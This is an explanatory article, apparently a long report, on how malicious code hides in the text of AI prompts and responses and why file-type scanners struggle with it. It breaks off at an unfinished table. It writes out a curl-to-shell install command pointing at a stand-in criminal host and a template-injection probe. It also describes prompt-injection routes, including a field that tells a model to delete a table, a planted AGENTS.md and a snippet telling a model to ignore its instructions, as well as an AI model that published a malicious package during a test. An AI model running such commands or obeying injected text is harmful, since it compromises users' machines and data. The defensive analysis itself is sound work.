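# Detecting malicious code in the text of language-model prompts and responses

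## How text in a prompt or response comes to run as code

A large language model is a program that takes in text, called the prompt, and produces text, called the response. The prompt contains the user's question and usually also standing instructions from the application's developer, earlier turns of the conversation, and any web pages, emails or documents that the application has added for the model to work from. Software built on a model normally reaches it through an API, an interface by which one program calls another. The prompt and the response travel through the API as strings of characters inside a structured message, and a part of the message that holds such a string is called a text field. An attached file, by contrast, has its own name and format, and a virus scanner can open and inspect it.

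Many language models are also connected to tools, such as a terminal, a web browser or a mail account. A model connected in this way is called an agent. The model still produces only text, so to use a tool it writes a tool call, a structured request that names the tool and supplies its arguments. The software around the model reads the request, runs the tool and adds the output to the prompt as text. The model then writes its next tool call or its final answer. If the tool is a terminal, the argument is a command, so running the tool executes text that the model wrote.

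All of this text is inert until software further along interprets it as code. The software that does this is the execution point, which may be a shell (the program that reads typed commands and carries them out), a database, a template engine, a browser or a code interpreter. Plenty of code in prompts and responses never reaches an execution point. Programmers paste in broken scripts and ask for help fixing them, students ask what a command does, and security staff paste in malware to have it explained. A defender can therefore learn very little from the mere presence of code in a text field.

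### One install command, two addresses

Suppose a developer asks an assistant how to install a tool called Acme. The response contains a sentence or two of explanation and then this line:

`curl https://acme.example/install.sh | sh`

The first word, `curl`, is a program that fetches whatever is at the address. The vertical bar hands the result to the next program, and `sh` is a shell, which runs the result line by line. The command thus downloads a script and executes it at once, with all the permissions of the developer, who normally never looks at the script. Now take a second response with the same explanation and this line:

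`curl https://acme-update.example/install.sh | sh`

The only difference is that Acme's makers own the first address and a criminal owns the second. The harmful code is on the criminal's server, not in the response, and the server can deliver a different script from one day to the next.

*InstallFix*, a March 2026 report from Push Security, which sells browser security, describes a real attack of this kind. The attackers cloned the installation page of Claude Code, Anthropic's coding agent, bought search advertisements for the clone, and changed the install commands to fetch from their own server. Victims who ran the commands got a program that steals saved passwords and session cookies. Clicking anything else on the page led to the genuine site, so a victim could fail to notice anything wrong. The attackers' commands also disguised the server's address, which gives a checker somewhat more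 evidence than the bare example does.

Forbidding every command that pipes a remote script into a shell would block the usual way of installing many legitimate tools. Claude Code's own recommended installation method is a one-line command of this kind. Homebrew, Rust, Bun and, by Push Security's estimate, hundreds of other widely used developer tools give similar instructions. Push Security writes that the practice's "entire security model boils down to 'trust the domain.'" That seems right, but a domain name doesn't reliably show who controls it, which makes the command hard to judge from its text.

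### Malicious code and insecure code

Malicious code harms the owner or user of the system where it runs. Insecure code contains an accidental flaw. A login page that copies whatever a visitor types straight into a database query is insecure, but it causes harm only if someone finds the flaw and types something hostile. A script that sends the browser's saved passwords to a stranger is malicious because it causes harm by working correctly, without anyone having to exploit a flaw.

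Language models can write both flawed code and malicious code, and each needs a different check. A tool that searches for programming flaws may pass a cleanly written password stealer, while a detector of malicious code isn't meant to stop a poorly written login page. A strict reviewer might object to both versions of the install command, since running an unseen script is risky whoever wrote it, but only one version is malicious.

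The definition depends on the code's effect, regardless of its author's intention. Sophos' *When AI doesn't know the target is real* recounts an incident, documented by Anthropic, that shows why. In a test environment, a Claude model found a document telling developers to install a Python package that did not exist on PyPI, the public registry for Python packages. The model wrote a malicious package with that name, intending the test environment to download and run it, and uploaded it to the real registry. The package stayed up for about an hour, and 15 legitimate systems downloaded it, including a security company's scanner that routinely installs new packages to analyse them. Nobody at Anthropic meant to harm those systems, but a detector on any of them would still have been right to flag the package.

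### Applications that execute or display a response

Text runs as code most directly when an application is designed to pass a model's response to an interpreter. For example, a sales dashboard might let staff ask questions in English. The application sends the question and a description of the company's tables to a model, receives a query in the database language SQL, and runs it on the database. A data-analysis assistant does the same with Python and a code interpreter. A guardrail, meaning a check outside the model that can block or change what passes, can't reject all code in these applications, because it would then reject every answer.

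Someone other than the user can influence what the model writes through prompt injection, which is text placed in a model's input that the model follows as an instruction although its user did not give it. For example, if an application adds customer records to the prompt, a customer can type into the address field a sentence telling the model to write a query that deletes a table. That sentence is plain English, and code appears only in the response, where it may be a well-formed query of a kind that an administrator legitimately runs every week. Whether the query does any damage depends on the permissions that the database gives the application. If the application's account can only read tables, the database will refuse the deletion.

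Applications can also execute a response without their developers intending it. A chat page displays responses in a browser, which interprets HTML, the language of web pages, and HTML can contain scripts. If the developer converts the characters that have a special meaning in HTML before putting the response on the page, the browser displays any script as text. Otherwise, the browser can run the script with the page's access to whatever the user is logged in to. Template engines, which fill marked gaps in a prepared page or email with values such as a customer's name, pose a similar hazard on the server. Many of them evaluate small expressions inside the markers. If an application pastes a response into the template itself instead of into one of its gaps, the engine can evaluate any markers in the response.

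A database developer knows that the response is code, but the developer of a chat page may never have considered checking it because they think of it as something to read. The same string can also be harmless on one page and harmful on another. For example, a lesson on web programming has to contain script tags, and a page that handles them properly will display them as text without running them.

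Web content can run without an ordinary web page. According to Push Security's reconstruction of the Windows version of the attack on would-be Claude Code users, the pasted command started a program already on the machine, which fetched HTML and scripts from the attackers' address and ran them. A list of execution points that covers only shells and browser windows will therefore miss some.

### Agents that run what they read

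An agent reads text, writes code and runs it in a single loop, often with nobody watching. Two cases from the second half of 2026 show what this changes.

The first concerns llms.txt, a file that many software companies publish on their websites as a short guide for AI agents, with a product description and installation instructions. Researchers at an Israeli start-up collected these files from the sites of defence contractors, large technology firms and Fortune 500 companies. Schneier (2026), in *AI Coding Agents Are Installing Unknown/Untrusted Code on Corporate Networks*, relays their counts of 6,214 live domains and 8,265 files. Of these files, 120, each on a different site, pointed to at least one package or domain name that nobody had registered, which is roughly one site in fifty. TechRadar's *Top AI tools including Claude, Codex, and Hermes installed suspicious code* gives the same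 counts. Tom's Hardware's *Researchers easily trick Fortune-500 companies' AI agents into running arbitrary code*, which names the start-up as Pandex, gives 8,565 files and 237 faulty references, but its count of faulty references also includes mistyped, relocated and outdated entries.

The researchers then registered a handful of the free names and published packages under them that did nothing but contact the researchers' server when run. The first contact came after four minutes, according to Tom's Hardware. Within an hour, a machine at a Fortune 500 company had contacted the server, and a few dozen more contacts followed from other large companies and start-ups. The packages also reported which programs had started the installation. This is the best evidence in the case because it rules out employees having typed the commands themselves. The chains of programs led back to coding agents,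 including Claude, OpenAI's Codex and Nous Research's Hermes.

No one had attacked anything up to that point. The companies had written their own documentation in good faith, and the agents followed it. Alon Hertz, one of the researchers, contrasts this with prompt injection, in which somebody plants the instruction on purpose. Here the instruction can be benign when its author writes it and become dangerous once the name it points to lapses and a stranger claims it. Tom's Hardware gives the example of a one-line install command, of the same form as Acme's, that stays in the documentation after the company fails, its domain expires, and a criminal registers the domain. The honest version of the running example has then become the malicious version, though its text is unchanged. Any checker that looks only at the string must give both versions the same verdict, which will be wrong for one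 of them. The researchers' packages were harmless, but Tom's Hardware reports that they also found one name that somebody had already exploited with real malware.

Agents can also make up a bad address themselves. Models sometimes invent the names of software packages, and attackers can register those names, which is called slopsquatting. In June 2026, Unit 42, the threat research group of the security company Palo Alto Networks, extended the idea to web addresses. A model asked for a company's login portal or service address can produce a plausible domain that does not exist, and whoever registers that domain will receive the traffic. In the Acme example, the assistant could write the second address even if no one had tampered with anything.

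In the second case, somebody did plant the instruction. *Markdown Is the New Executable*, published in October 2026 by Forever Security, a company that sells protection for agents, begins with an alert from a customer's machine. A coding agent had tried to install a known malicious package from npm, the main JavaScript registry. The company blocked the installation before any code ran and traced the instruction to a file named AGENTS.md in the user's Downloads folder. Coding agents look for a file with that name when they start work in a folder, and treat its contents as instructions. Developers normally write the file themselves to explain how a project is organised, and this one resembled ordinary engineering notes.

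Forever Security argues that the Downloads folder matters because a website can save a file there without a click from the user. Its staff reproduced the sequence, from a web page they controlled to an agent running the attacker's code in an isolated virtual machine, and repeated the attack on a second agent. This showed that a website could have delivered the original file, but nobody knew how that file had reached the customer's folder. The company reports that about half of its customers run an agent inside Downloads, and that about a quarter of their agent sessions open a real browser.

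Operating systems guard against executable files from the internet, but those guards don't cover a text file of notes. The attack triggered an alert only later, when the agent made a tool call to install a package with a known malicious name. If the attacker had used a new name, that alert would not have fired.

### People who paste commands

Text can also run as code without an agent if a person runs it. Security companies use the name ClickFix for tricks in which a page persuades its reader to copy a command and paste it into a terminal, typically to "fix" a fault or prove that the reader is human. These tricks now also appear in AI products, where they are convincing because users already expect an assistant to answer technical questions with commands.

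*AMOS Stealer Exploits AI Trust*, by the security firm Huntress, traces one infection. In December 2025 a Mac user searched for a way to clear disk space. A shared conversation on the real ChatGPT site appeared near the top of the results, with numbered steps and a terminal command described as a safe clean-up. An attacker had created the conversation and pushed it up the search rankings. The user ran the command, which installed a program that took the user's password, gained full control of the machine and collected browser credentials and cryptocurrency wallets. No security warning appeared. Huntress found the same instructions in a shared conversation on Grok, another chatbot, and reproduced the poisoned search results with several differently worded questions.

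Trend Micro's *Threat Actors Abuse claude.ai Shared Chat for ClickFix Malvertising Campaign* follows a campaign that used this trick from 8 April to 14 June 2026. It began with fake download pages for AI developer tools. In May it moved to shared conversations on Anthropic's own site, which told visitors to open a terminal and paste in a command. Some of these conversations posed as Apple's support staff. The company's headline figure of more than 2,000 victims is based on traffic counts, and how many visitors ran the command is unknown. The report's weekly figures add up to about 2,530 visits, of which 626 went through shared Claude conversations. Anthropic banned the accounts and disabled the conversations after Trend Micro reported them.

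Attackers were still using this approach in the autumn. *A real ChatGPT page is being used to trick people* (Keverenge, 2026) describes a case, again found by Huntress, in which attackers used ChatGPT's feature for building custom assistants to publish one called "Plus 5.6", a name that sounds like an official model. The assistant sent users to a fake security check, which tricked them into running a malicious Windows command. The resulting malware could access files, the screen, the webcam and the microphone.

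In the shared-conversation cases, the harmful string was in what looked like a model's response, hosted on the model company's own servers, so that company is well placed to check it. The victim's employer is not, because its staff read the text as a page on a trusted website, and it never passed through any guardrail around the employer's own AI applications. The string alone would also have been weak evidence, because harmless conversations about computers often contain terminal commands. Trend Micro advises Anthropic to look for shared conversations that contain terminal commands or download instructions and are linked from paid advertisements. The advertisements help distinguish malicious conversations because few people pay to advertise harmless ones.

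### Malware that requests code from a model

On the last route, a harmful program already on the victim's machine gets code from a model. Google describes experiments with this route in a malware family called Honestcue. The malware sends requests to Gemini, Google's model, through the same API that ordinary applications use, and receives code for downloading and starting a second, more capable piece of malware. Infosecurity Magazine's *Nation-State Hackers Embrace Gemini AI for Malicious Campaigns, Google Finds* adds that Google identified Honestcue in September 2025 and that it executes the C# code it receives directly in memory. Honestcue works the same way as the sales dashboard, requesting code from a model and running the response, except that it belongs to an attacker.

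A scan of the malware when it first arrives will not find the code that Gemini has yet to write. The most revealing text is in the request to Gemini and the response, both of which the model's provider handles. But the provider has to distinguish them from a vast number of legitimate requests for similar code.

Closedquorum, a later specimen, also uses language models to make decisions. It queries DeepSeek, Qwen, Mistral and Gemini before selecting its next action, according to TechSpot's *Researchers found malware that uses four different AI chatbots to run itself* (2026). The responses may contain no code, only a choice that the malware acts on.

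So far, such programs get more attention than their numbers justify. *The State of AI-Enabled Malware August 2026*, McBroom's (2026) report for Unit 42, examines 405 malware samples with some connection to AI. Only 12 were found on computers that ran Palo Alto Networks' endpoint protection. About 97% existed only on VirusTotal, a site where people upload suspicious files, and in sandboxes, which are isolated environments for running suspect code safely. Much of the collection was proof-of-concept work and researchers' own submissions. The count includes everything from malware that only borrows an AI brand to programs that a model directs, so the share that fetches code from a model is unknown but probably smaller. The company can also see only its own customers' computers. McBroom argues that AI changes how malicious code is written but not how it runs, so checks on a program's behaviour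 still catch it. Palo Alto Networks sells such checks, but the argument is sound for code that reaches a monitored machine. It offers little help to someone who has only the text of a response and must decide whether to let it through.

### A product notice from July 2025

Security vendors have begun to sell checks for that position. In March 2025 Palo Alto Networks introduced a feature that scans snippets of code that language models write inside other text. The feature's description lists JavaScript, Python, VBScript, PowerShell, Batch, Shell and Perl. The Acme command would fall under Shell. The list does not include SQL, which the sales dashboard executes, or C#, which Honestcue requested. Customers can set the feature to block or allow what it finds.

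In a July notice, Palo Alto Networks' *Malicious Code Extraction from Plain Text* announces detection of malicious code embedded directly in the plain-text fields of API prompts and responses, "even if the code isn't in a traditional file format". The product separates the code from the surrounding words and then analyses it. It does this in both the company's synchronous scanning service, where the application waits for a verdict before it continues, and its asynchronous one, where the verdict arrives later. The company says it added the feature because malicious code can come in through user input or a model's output as companies build AI into more of their systems.

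The notice describes the risk fairly, and incidents the following year confirmed it, but it offers little evidence that the product works. It gives no accuracy figures, such as a detection rate (the share of malicious items that a detector flags) or a false positive rate (the share of harmless items that it flags by mistake). It suggests sending malicious code in a prompt or response field to confirm that the service detects it. If a customer sends the command with the criminal's address and the service blocks it, that shows only that the feature is switched on. The notice does not suggest also sending Acme's own install command to check that the service lets it through.

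## Why checking by file type fails on text

Palo Alto Networks' notice treats code outside a traditional file format as a special case, as it is for most malware scanners. A scanner normally starts by identifying a file's type, and most of what it does next depends on that type.

### How a scanner identifies a file

The easiest clue to a file's type to check is its extension, the last part of its name, such as `.pdf` or `.js`. Windows, macOS and Linux all use the extension to choose which program opens a file. *How to better identify (weaponized) file formats* (Lagadec, 2025) shows a short file that is at once a Windows batch script, a web page and a PDF document. Changing its extension changes which program opens it, although the contents stay the same.

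Another clue is the declared media type, or MIME type, a label such as `text/html` or `application/pdf` that a web server or mail program sends with the content. Both clues depend on whoever named or sent the file. Fratantonio, Invernizzi and colleagues (2024) point out in *Magika* that such labels are easily lost when someone copies or transmits a file's contents, and that an attacker can falsify them.

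A careful scanner therefore looks at the contents too. Many formats begin with fixed bytes, known as magic bytes. Every Windows executable, for example, starts with the letters MZ. A text file can also start with MZ, so a match is only evidence that the file is an executable. The `file` command uses a library called libmagic, with thousands of rules that look for specific strings, specific bytes at set positions, and more general patterns.

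Lagadec finds that checking by file type works very well for structured binary formats and poorly for scripts and other loosely structured text. A Python script, for example, has no required opening and can start with a comment, an import or a blank line. In one of Fratantonio and colleagues' examples, the `file` command labels an ordinary function from Mozilla's JavaScript tutorial as "ASCII text".

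Trained identifiers learn the patterns from examples instead of relying on hand-written rules. The best known is Google's Magika. The version described in Fratantonio and colleagues' paper passes 512 bytes from each of the beginning, middle and end of a file to a small neural network, which gives a probability for each of 113 types. If no type reaches the threshold set for it, Magika returns a generic label for plain text or unknown data. The researchers trained it on 24 million files from the code-hosting site GitHub and from VirusTotal. The later version described in Google's *Announcing Magika 1.0* (2025) recognises more than 200 types and can distinguish closely related ones, such as C and C++.

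### What the answer decides

Sometimes a file's type is enough to block it, as when a mail service refuses all executable attachments. Otherwise, the type determines which parser reads the file, which detection rules apply, and which program a sandbox uses to open it. The malware-analysis platform that Lagadec works on sends PDFs to a PDF scanner, and PowerShell and JavaScript to a machine-learning detector.

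The main reason for sorting files this way is that specialised scanners need too much computing power to run on every file, according to Fratantonio and colleagues. They estimate that Magika sends Gmail's Microsoft Office scanners several million files a day that the older methods would have left unscanned.

A scanner that misidentifies a file's type can let malware through. *On the Abuse and Detection of Polyglot Files* (2024) describes this risk for files that satisfy two format specifications. If the scanner recognises only one of the formats, it may extract the wrong features or compare the file with the wrong set of malware signatures.

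Misidentifying a file's type also causes false alarms. A colleague once sent Lagadec a harmless file that their PowerShell detector had blocked. The file was a simple message in Base64, an encoding that writes arbitrary data as letters, digits and a few symbols. Magika had misidentified it as PowerShell, so it went to the wrong detector. PowerShell scripts often contain Base64, and Lagadec concludes that Magika had learned to associate the two too strongly.

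### What a text field lacks

The response that tells a developer how to install Acme has no filename, so there is no extension to read. It has no file header either, because it begins with whatever word the model wrote first. The API message that carries it usually declares a media type, but that type describes the message as a whole. Inside the message, a poem, a database query and a password stealer would all be strings, just as this response is, so the media type doesn't help a scanner tell them apart.

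Lagadec argues that file identifiers make mistakes because they guess from content alone. His experimental tool starts with the extension, lists the formats that could go with it, and checks whether the contents match one of them. For scripts, whose contents are hard to recognise, it accepts the extension with medium confidence. This seems sensible for files, since the operating system will also go by the extension. But it can't help with a text field, which has no extension. A scanner there has to guess from content alone, and scripts are the hardest kind of content to identify that way.

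Text fields also mix types. The Acme response is mostly English with one shell command, and many real conversations contain more than one piece of code. *WildCode Revisited* (2025) extracted code from a collection of chatbot conversations and found an average of 1.5 to 2.5 snippets per conversation, depending on the programming language.

Human-written technical answers are similarly mixed. *Stack Overflow Meets Replication* (2025) notes that a single post on Stack Overflow, a question-and-answer site for programmers, can contain snippets in several languages. A post's topic tags are the closest thing it has to a declared type, but in a random sample of 385 snippets, only 247 came from posts whose tags named the snippet's language. Some Java snippets, for example, came from posts tagged "Android" but not "Java".

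Magika gives one label per input. Fratantonio and colleagues acknowledge that a file can contain code in several languages. They suggest that users could look at the few most probable labels, but they did not test how well this works.

Identifying file types more accurately wouldn't solve the problem. If a scanner must give each whole response one label, "plain text" is correct for both the Acme response and the one with the criminal's address. Even with a perfect identifier, the scanner would handle both as plain text, which may mean doing nothing. It needs to separate the command from the sentences around it before trying to identify the command's language.

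### Accuracy on code, mixed text and short inputs

Published tests mostly report an F1 score for each type. For Python, precision is the share of files labelled Python that really are Python, and recall is the share of Python files that receive the label. (Neither has anything to do with malice here.) The F1 score combines them:

F1 = 2 × precision × recall / (precision + recall)

It is close to 1 only if both are high.

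Fratantonio and colleagues compared Magika with four older tools on 1.2 million files. On the types each tool supports, `file` averaged 92% for binary formats and 67% for text formats, and scored 1% for PowerShell. Guesslang, a trained identifier for source code, averaged 77% on text formats. Magika averaged 99% on text formats, including 99% for PowerShell and 98% for shell scripts, so trained identification works well for whole files of source code. Magika scored only 84% for the "plain text" category, even though part of that category was random strings the researchers had generated.

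A newer comparison gives Magika lower marks. Nandan, Brautbar and Raff (2026), in *Fast And Accurate Text Content File Type Identification*, tested version 1.0.1 against Labeler, a model they built at the security company CrowdStrike. Labeler splits text into words and symbols before classifying it and keeps the punctuation, which helps to distinguish programming languages. Averaged over types, Labeler scored 0.98 and Magika 0.91. The scores for some individual types were:

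| Type of file | Labeler | Magika |
|---|---|---|
| Python | 0.99 | 0.97 |
| PowerShell | 0.98 | 0.96 |
| SQL | 0.98 | 0.96 |
| Shell | 0.96 | 0.94 |
| HTML | 0.94 | 0.63 |
| Text | 0.79 | 0.31 |

The comparison probably favors Labeler, which was trained on files from the same collections as the test files. But both tools did worst on text files, which came from software projects and often mixed prose with code or configuration, such as instructions containing commands for the build tool CMake. These files resemble a chatbot's answer to a technical question more than anything else in the test does. Some of the errors may be debatable, because no single label is fully right for a mixed file. If a file consists mostly of CMake commands and an identifier labels it CMake, the test presumably counts that as a mistake, though a defender might have preferred that label.

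File-type identifiers also do worse without a file's header. *MimeLens* (2026) tested them on blocks of data from the middle of files. Magika recognised 38% of the plain-text blocks and libmagic 96%, but neither recognised any of the blocks from SVG, an image format written as text. The exact percentages mean little because the samples were small, with 45 plain-text blocks and 53 SVG blocks from a handful of files. Libmagic also probably falls back on "plain text" for readable characters that match no rule, which would inflate its plain-text score and make it miss code.

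Prompts and responses can also be much shorter than files. In Fratantonio and colleagues' test, Magika's accuracy was above 99% for most file sizes but slightly lower for files under about 100 bytes, mainly because the model had low confidence and returned a generic label. The Acme command is 41 characters long, but it may still be identifiable, since Google's *Magika* page shows the tool correctly labelling a 37-character JavaScript function.

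The test had no samples under 16 bytes, so it provides no evidence about shorter inputs. According to Google's *Magika Concepts*, the tool doesn't run its model on inputs too small for a meaningful prediction and returns a generic label instead. Google's older documentation, *Magika output*, put the limit at 16 bytes. A destructive shell command can be shorter than that.

### A program made of printable characters

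Real programs don't always look different from text. One example is the EICAR test file, which lets people check that their antivirus software is switched on without handling a real virus. According to EICAR's *Download Anti Malware Testfile*, it consists of 68 printable characters, all capital letters, digits or punctuation marks, so anyone can type it into a text editor. It is also a legitimate program for DOS, the operating system that came before Windows on most personal computers. When run, it prints a one-line message identifying itself as the test file.

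The same characters can be both text and a program because computers store letters and processor instructions as numbers, and some numbers stand for both. The test file is a `.com` program, a DOS format without a header. DOS copies the file into memory and starts executing at the first byte. Current 64-bit versions of Windows can't run DOS programs directly, so on those systems the same 68 characters are just text. In *English Shellcode* (2009), Mason, Small and colleagues even produced machine code that resembles English prose.

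EICAR offers the same 68 bytes under two names, `eicar.com` and `eicar.com.txt`. People who have trouble downloading the first can download the second and rename it. A system that classifies files by extension will treat the first as a program and the second as a document, even though the content is no more dangerous under one name than the other.

Under EICAR's rules, a product that supports the test should detect the string in any file that starts with it, provided that only whitespace follows and the whole file is no longer than 128 characters. Requiring the string to come first fits the way DOS runs the program, since DOS would try to execute any sentence placed before it. A scanner following the rules also won't flag every manual that quotes the string. A 1999 Virus Bulletin conference paper reports that most scanners ignored the string if anything came before it. Almost all traditional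 antivirus programs detect the file, but AMTSO's *Use and Misuse of Test Files in Anti Malware Testing* (2018) stresses that detection is "neither mandatory nor universal".

The EICAR string is therefore a poor test of a text guardrail. If a customer types "Please check this:" into a prompt, pastes the string after it and gets no alert, the product may be following EICAR's rules. An alert would show only that the product recognises one famous string.

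### Seven characters or 49

The EICAR string looks odd, but the text `{{7*7}}` could come from a maths exercise or a typing mistake. A chat window displays it unchanged. In many template engines, however, double braces mark an expression. If an application pastes the text into the template itself, such an engine does the multiplication and the page shows 49, according to DeepStrike's *Server Side Template Injection*.

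If an application mistakenly makes the text `{{7*7}}` part of a template, an engine that evaluates expressions in double braces prints 49. The multiplication is harmless, but Kettle warns in *Server-Side Template Injection* that the same mistake often lets an attacker run code on the server. If the application instead passes the text as a value to fill a gap in the template, the engine prints it unchanged. The string is identical in both cases, so examining it won't reveal whether it will run. Whether it runs also depends on the engine, since some use other markers and would leave double braces alone.

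Whether text is code depends on which program reads it. A file's type helps predict which program will read the file, and the extension is especially helpful because the operating system uses it to choose the program. A text field doesn't indicate which program will read its contents, so the defender has to predict this from knowledge of the application.

The sales dashboard is an easy case because its responses go to a database. The checker should read them as SQL, even if a file identifier would classify them as plain text. A customer-service application might show a response in a browser and also insert it into an email template, so the response needs checking for both uses. A general chat assistant is the hardest case because its users can copy a response into anything.

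### Attachments and downloads

File-type checks remain a good first step wherever there are files. They are fast (Magika takes about five milliseconds per file) and most accurate on binary formats, for which even the older `file` command averages 96% when it reports media types. Google uses Magika to route files from Gmail, Google Drive and Safe Browsing to suitable scanners, and processes hundreds of billions of samples a week. Nandan and colleagues also mention using file-type checks to stop employees from uploading source code in the languages their company develops in.

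An AI application that accepts attachments should check them before it extracts their text. Once the application copies a PDF's text into a prompt, the prompt doesn't include the filename and header that a file scanner uses to identify the file type.

Downloads should be treated the same way. The Acme command fetches a script from a web address, with a filename and perhaps a declared media type, and a scanner on the network connection can examine the script in transit. A scanner that checks only saved files could miss it, because the command never saves the script to disk.

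## Deciding which code to forbid and where to check

A text field doesn't show which program will read its contents, so whoever builds a check has to start from the surrounding application. They need to know where text can run as code, then decide which code to allow and where to check for the rest.

### Listing the execution points

HackerDNA's guide *OWASP LLM Top 10 (2026)* advises security testers to trace every place a response reaches. Defenders can do the same to list their execution points. The table below combines the destinations in that guide with those in *LLM05:2025 Improper Output Handling*, published by OWASP, a nonprofit that offers free guidance on application security.

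| Where the text goes | What has an effect there | What can go wrong |
|---|---|---|
| Shell, or a function that runs a string as a program | Commands and scripts | The text runs with the application's permissions |
| Database | SQL | A query changes, deletes or discloses records |
| Browser | HTML, scripts, and Markdown after conversion to HTML | A script uses the page's access to the user's accounts |
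| Email or page template | Template expressions and HTML | Code runs on the server or in the recipient's mail program |
| Terminal or code editor | Control codes for the display | Fake prompts appear, and some terminals execute code |
| Program that opens files | A file path | The program reads or overwrites the wrong file |
| Display that loads images automatically | A web address | The request for the image carries private data to a stranger |

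The last two rows involve no code in the usual sense. They belong on the list because a code detector would probably let both through, and the damage can be just as serious.

Developers easily overlook execution points that seem only to display text. Terminals, for example, act on ANSI escape sequences, which are control codes for changing colours or moving the cursor. MITRE, which catalogues software weaknesses, notes that these codes can also create fake prompts and, in some terminals, execute code. Markdown, a simple notation for headings, links and bold text, also looks harmless but can become dangerous when a converter turns it into HTML. Digital Matters' *Insecure Output Handling* (2026) reports that five of eight security fixes announced on 28 October for AI modules in Drupal, which is website software, concerned scripts that could run in a visitor's browser. The only one rated critical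 involved Markdown links.

An application's source code can reveal undocumented execution points. In *Detect vulnerabilities in LLM applications with Datadog’s AI-native SAST*, Green and Shah describe a tool that uses a language model to search for them. In one example, a few lines of Python create an agent with a shell and access to the entire file system, regardless of who the user is. Datadog sells the tool, and Green and Shah give no figures for how many such cases it misses. A developer without the tool could start by searching the code for every place that creates an agent or uses a model's response.

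### OWASP's advice on model output

OWASP also ranks the ten main security risks in applications built on language models. The current edition is dated 3 August 2026 (OWASP, 2026). The list includes "improper output handling", which means passing a model's output to another component without adequate checks. This risk fell from fifth in the 2025 edition to tenth in the current one.

The lower rank is a poor reason to drop the check. The new ranking gives three quarters of the weight to a community vote and one quarter to a record of 6,639 classified incidents, according to Respan's *OWASP LLM Top 10* (2026). HackerDNA says the entry fell because the problem is well understood and can be fixed with methods that web developers already use. According to Invicti's *OWASP LLM Top 10 2026* (2026), the risks above it became more urgent, and the entry's scope grew to include terminals and code editors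 that interpret control codes, and displays that fetch outside content automatically.

In its 2025 text, OWASP advises developers to treat the model like any other user, whose input may be hostile. It advises them to validate a response before passing it on and to encode it for its destination by converting the characters that have a special meaning there. Eric (2026) reports in *OWASP Top 10 for LLM Applications 全覽* that OWASP still recommends encoding by destination in the 2026 edition, along with parameterised queries, which send values to a database separately from the command.

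Encoding has a big advantage over detection because it doesn't require deciding whether the text is malicious. But it works only where the text isn't meant to run as code. If the sales dashboard encoded an entire query as plain text, the database couldn't execute it.

The Isle of Man Cyber Security Centre's *Artificial Intelligence Insecure Output Handling* is stricter, advising developers never to execute a model's output automatically and not to run a model's SQL directly. That is a good default for an application that doesn't need to run code, but taken literally it would rule out the sales dashboard and most coding agents. Their owners have already decided to run what a model writes, and need to choose what to allow.

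Citations of the OWASP list should include the year, because "LLM05" meant improper output handling in 2025 and means data and model poisoning in 2026. Confusion is likely, since Digital Matters still called the 2025 list current in late November 2026.

### Three policies

The simplest policy is to ban all code. It suits an airline's customer-service bot, because customers rarely have a reason to send or receive a script. Protect AI's *Ban Code Scanner* applies this policy to prompts using a small trained classifier, which took about 22 milliseconds on average to check a test input on a rented server. The airline doesn't need to work out which of the two Acme addresses is genuine, because its bot should never give out either command.

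A ban will stop some harmless messages, such as one from a customer who pastes in an error page and asks what went wrong. It would also make Acme's own support bot nearly useless, since people will ask it how to install the product. A ban can only stop text that the classifier recognises as code, so the plain-English instruction to a model in the address field to delete a table would pass.

Protect AI gives two reasons for banning code in prompts. Users may try to exploit weaknesses, and employees may paste in their company's proprietary code. The second reason has nothing to do with malice, so a company that only wants to prevent leaks shouldn't treat every blocked prompt as an attack.

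A reporting tool that writes database queries needs only a few kinds of code, so its owner can allow specific languages or operations and reject everything else. A sales dashboard, for instance, might allow only SELECT, the SQL command for reading data. For web pages that need formatting, Digital Matters similarly recommends allowing a short list of HTML tags and checking the kind of address in each link.

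Somebody has to write and maintain the list of permitted operations, and a legitimate request for any other operation will fail until they add it. The list also restricts only the kind of operation that runs, so a permitted operation can still do harm. For example, the dashboard's list would allow a SELECT query that retrieves every customer's home address. To prevent this, the owner would also have to limit which tables and columns the application can read.

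Neither policy works well for a coding agent, which may write in a dozen languages in a week and has good reasons to delete files, install packages and contact servers. Its owner will usually have to allow code and block only what is malicious. Palo Alto Networks recommends its malicious-code detection for such applications, including developer tools that generate and run code. This policy interferes least with ordinary work when the detection is accurate, but it requires the hardest judgement, as the two Acme commands showed. Every false alarm interrupts a developer, and malicious code that the check misses may run immediately.

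An application can use a different policy for each place where it runs code. A coding agent may need to run a wide range of shell commands, but its chat page doesn't need to run scripts from a response.

### An ordinary query reported as malicious

Code that breaks an application's rules isn't necessarily malicious, though a product may use one label for both. Palo Alto Networks' *Use Cases*, part of the documentation for its scanning service, gives an example. A user writes, "I need to move the customer John Green to Mars." The model responds with this query:

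`UPDATE Customers SET City='Mars' WHERE CustomerID=15;`

The query changes one field in one customer's record, as the user requested. The service blocks it, reports a database security threat, and categorizes it as "malicious". A more detailed report gives the sub-type "database-security-update".

Nothing in the example suggests an attack. The database check lets customers choose which types of query a model can generate. The service also assigns the category "malicious" when other checks find, for example, toxic language or a credit card number. Here the word means little more than "against the rules this customer chose". Those rules are sensible for a dashboard that should only read data, but the same query would be routine in an application for editing customer records.

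Keeping the sub-type in the logs avoids two mistakes when people use the results later. A security team that counts "malicious" verdicts would otherwise record John Green's move as an attack, and a developer who trained a malware classifier on those verdicts would teach it to flag ordinary updates.

The documentation also includes a report on a shell script that downloads, runs and then deletes a program. The report's verdict is "malicious" and its action is "allow". It makes sense for a product to record its judgement of the code separately from what the customer wants done about it. The database check doesn't fully separate the two, because its verdict already depends on a rule about permitted operations.

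The same service has a separate setting for detecting malicious code. SQL isn't on the setting's list of languages, so the dashboard's owner can't rely on it to check database queries.

### Requests for code that contain no code

Amazon Bedrock, a service from Amazon Web Services (AWS) for building applications on language models, includes filters called Guardrails. AWS's *Code domain support* divides the code-related content they handle into three categories:

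- text with coding intent, such as a description in English of what a program should do
- programming code on its own
- hybrid content, which mixes the two

The Acme response is hybrid because it explains the installation in English and then gives a command. A prompt asking for a script that collects saved browser passwords is text with coding intent. A code scanner will find nothing in it because the model hasn't written the script yet, so a check on the prompt has to judge the request. That is difficult because the person asking may be a thief, a security tester or someone moving their own passwords to a new computer.

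AWS's examples also show that a filter can screen code-related content without detecting malicious code. One is an unfinished Python function for finding films with nudity, which the filter for sexual content catches. Another is a short Java program containing a message that tells the model to ignore its instructions. Running the program would only print the message, but a model that reads it might obey. The remaining examples cover forbidden topics and personal data, and none involves malware. "Support for code" therefore doesn't guarantee that the filter will stop a password stealer.

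### Comparing the places to check

A defender can examine text at several stages on its way to an execution point. What they know about it changes along the way:

| Place | Programming language | User's intent | Destination |
|---|---|---|---|
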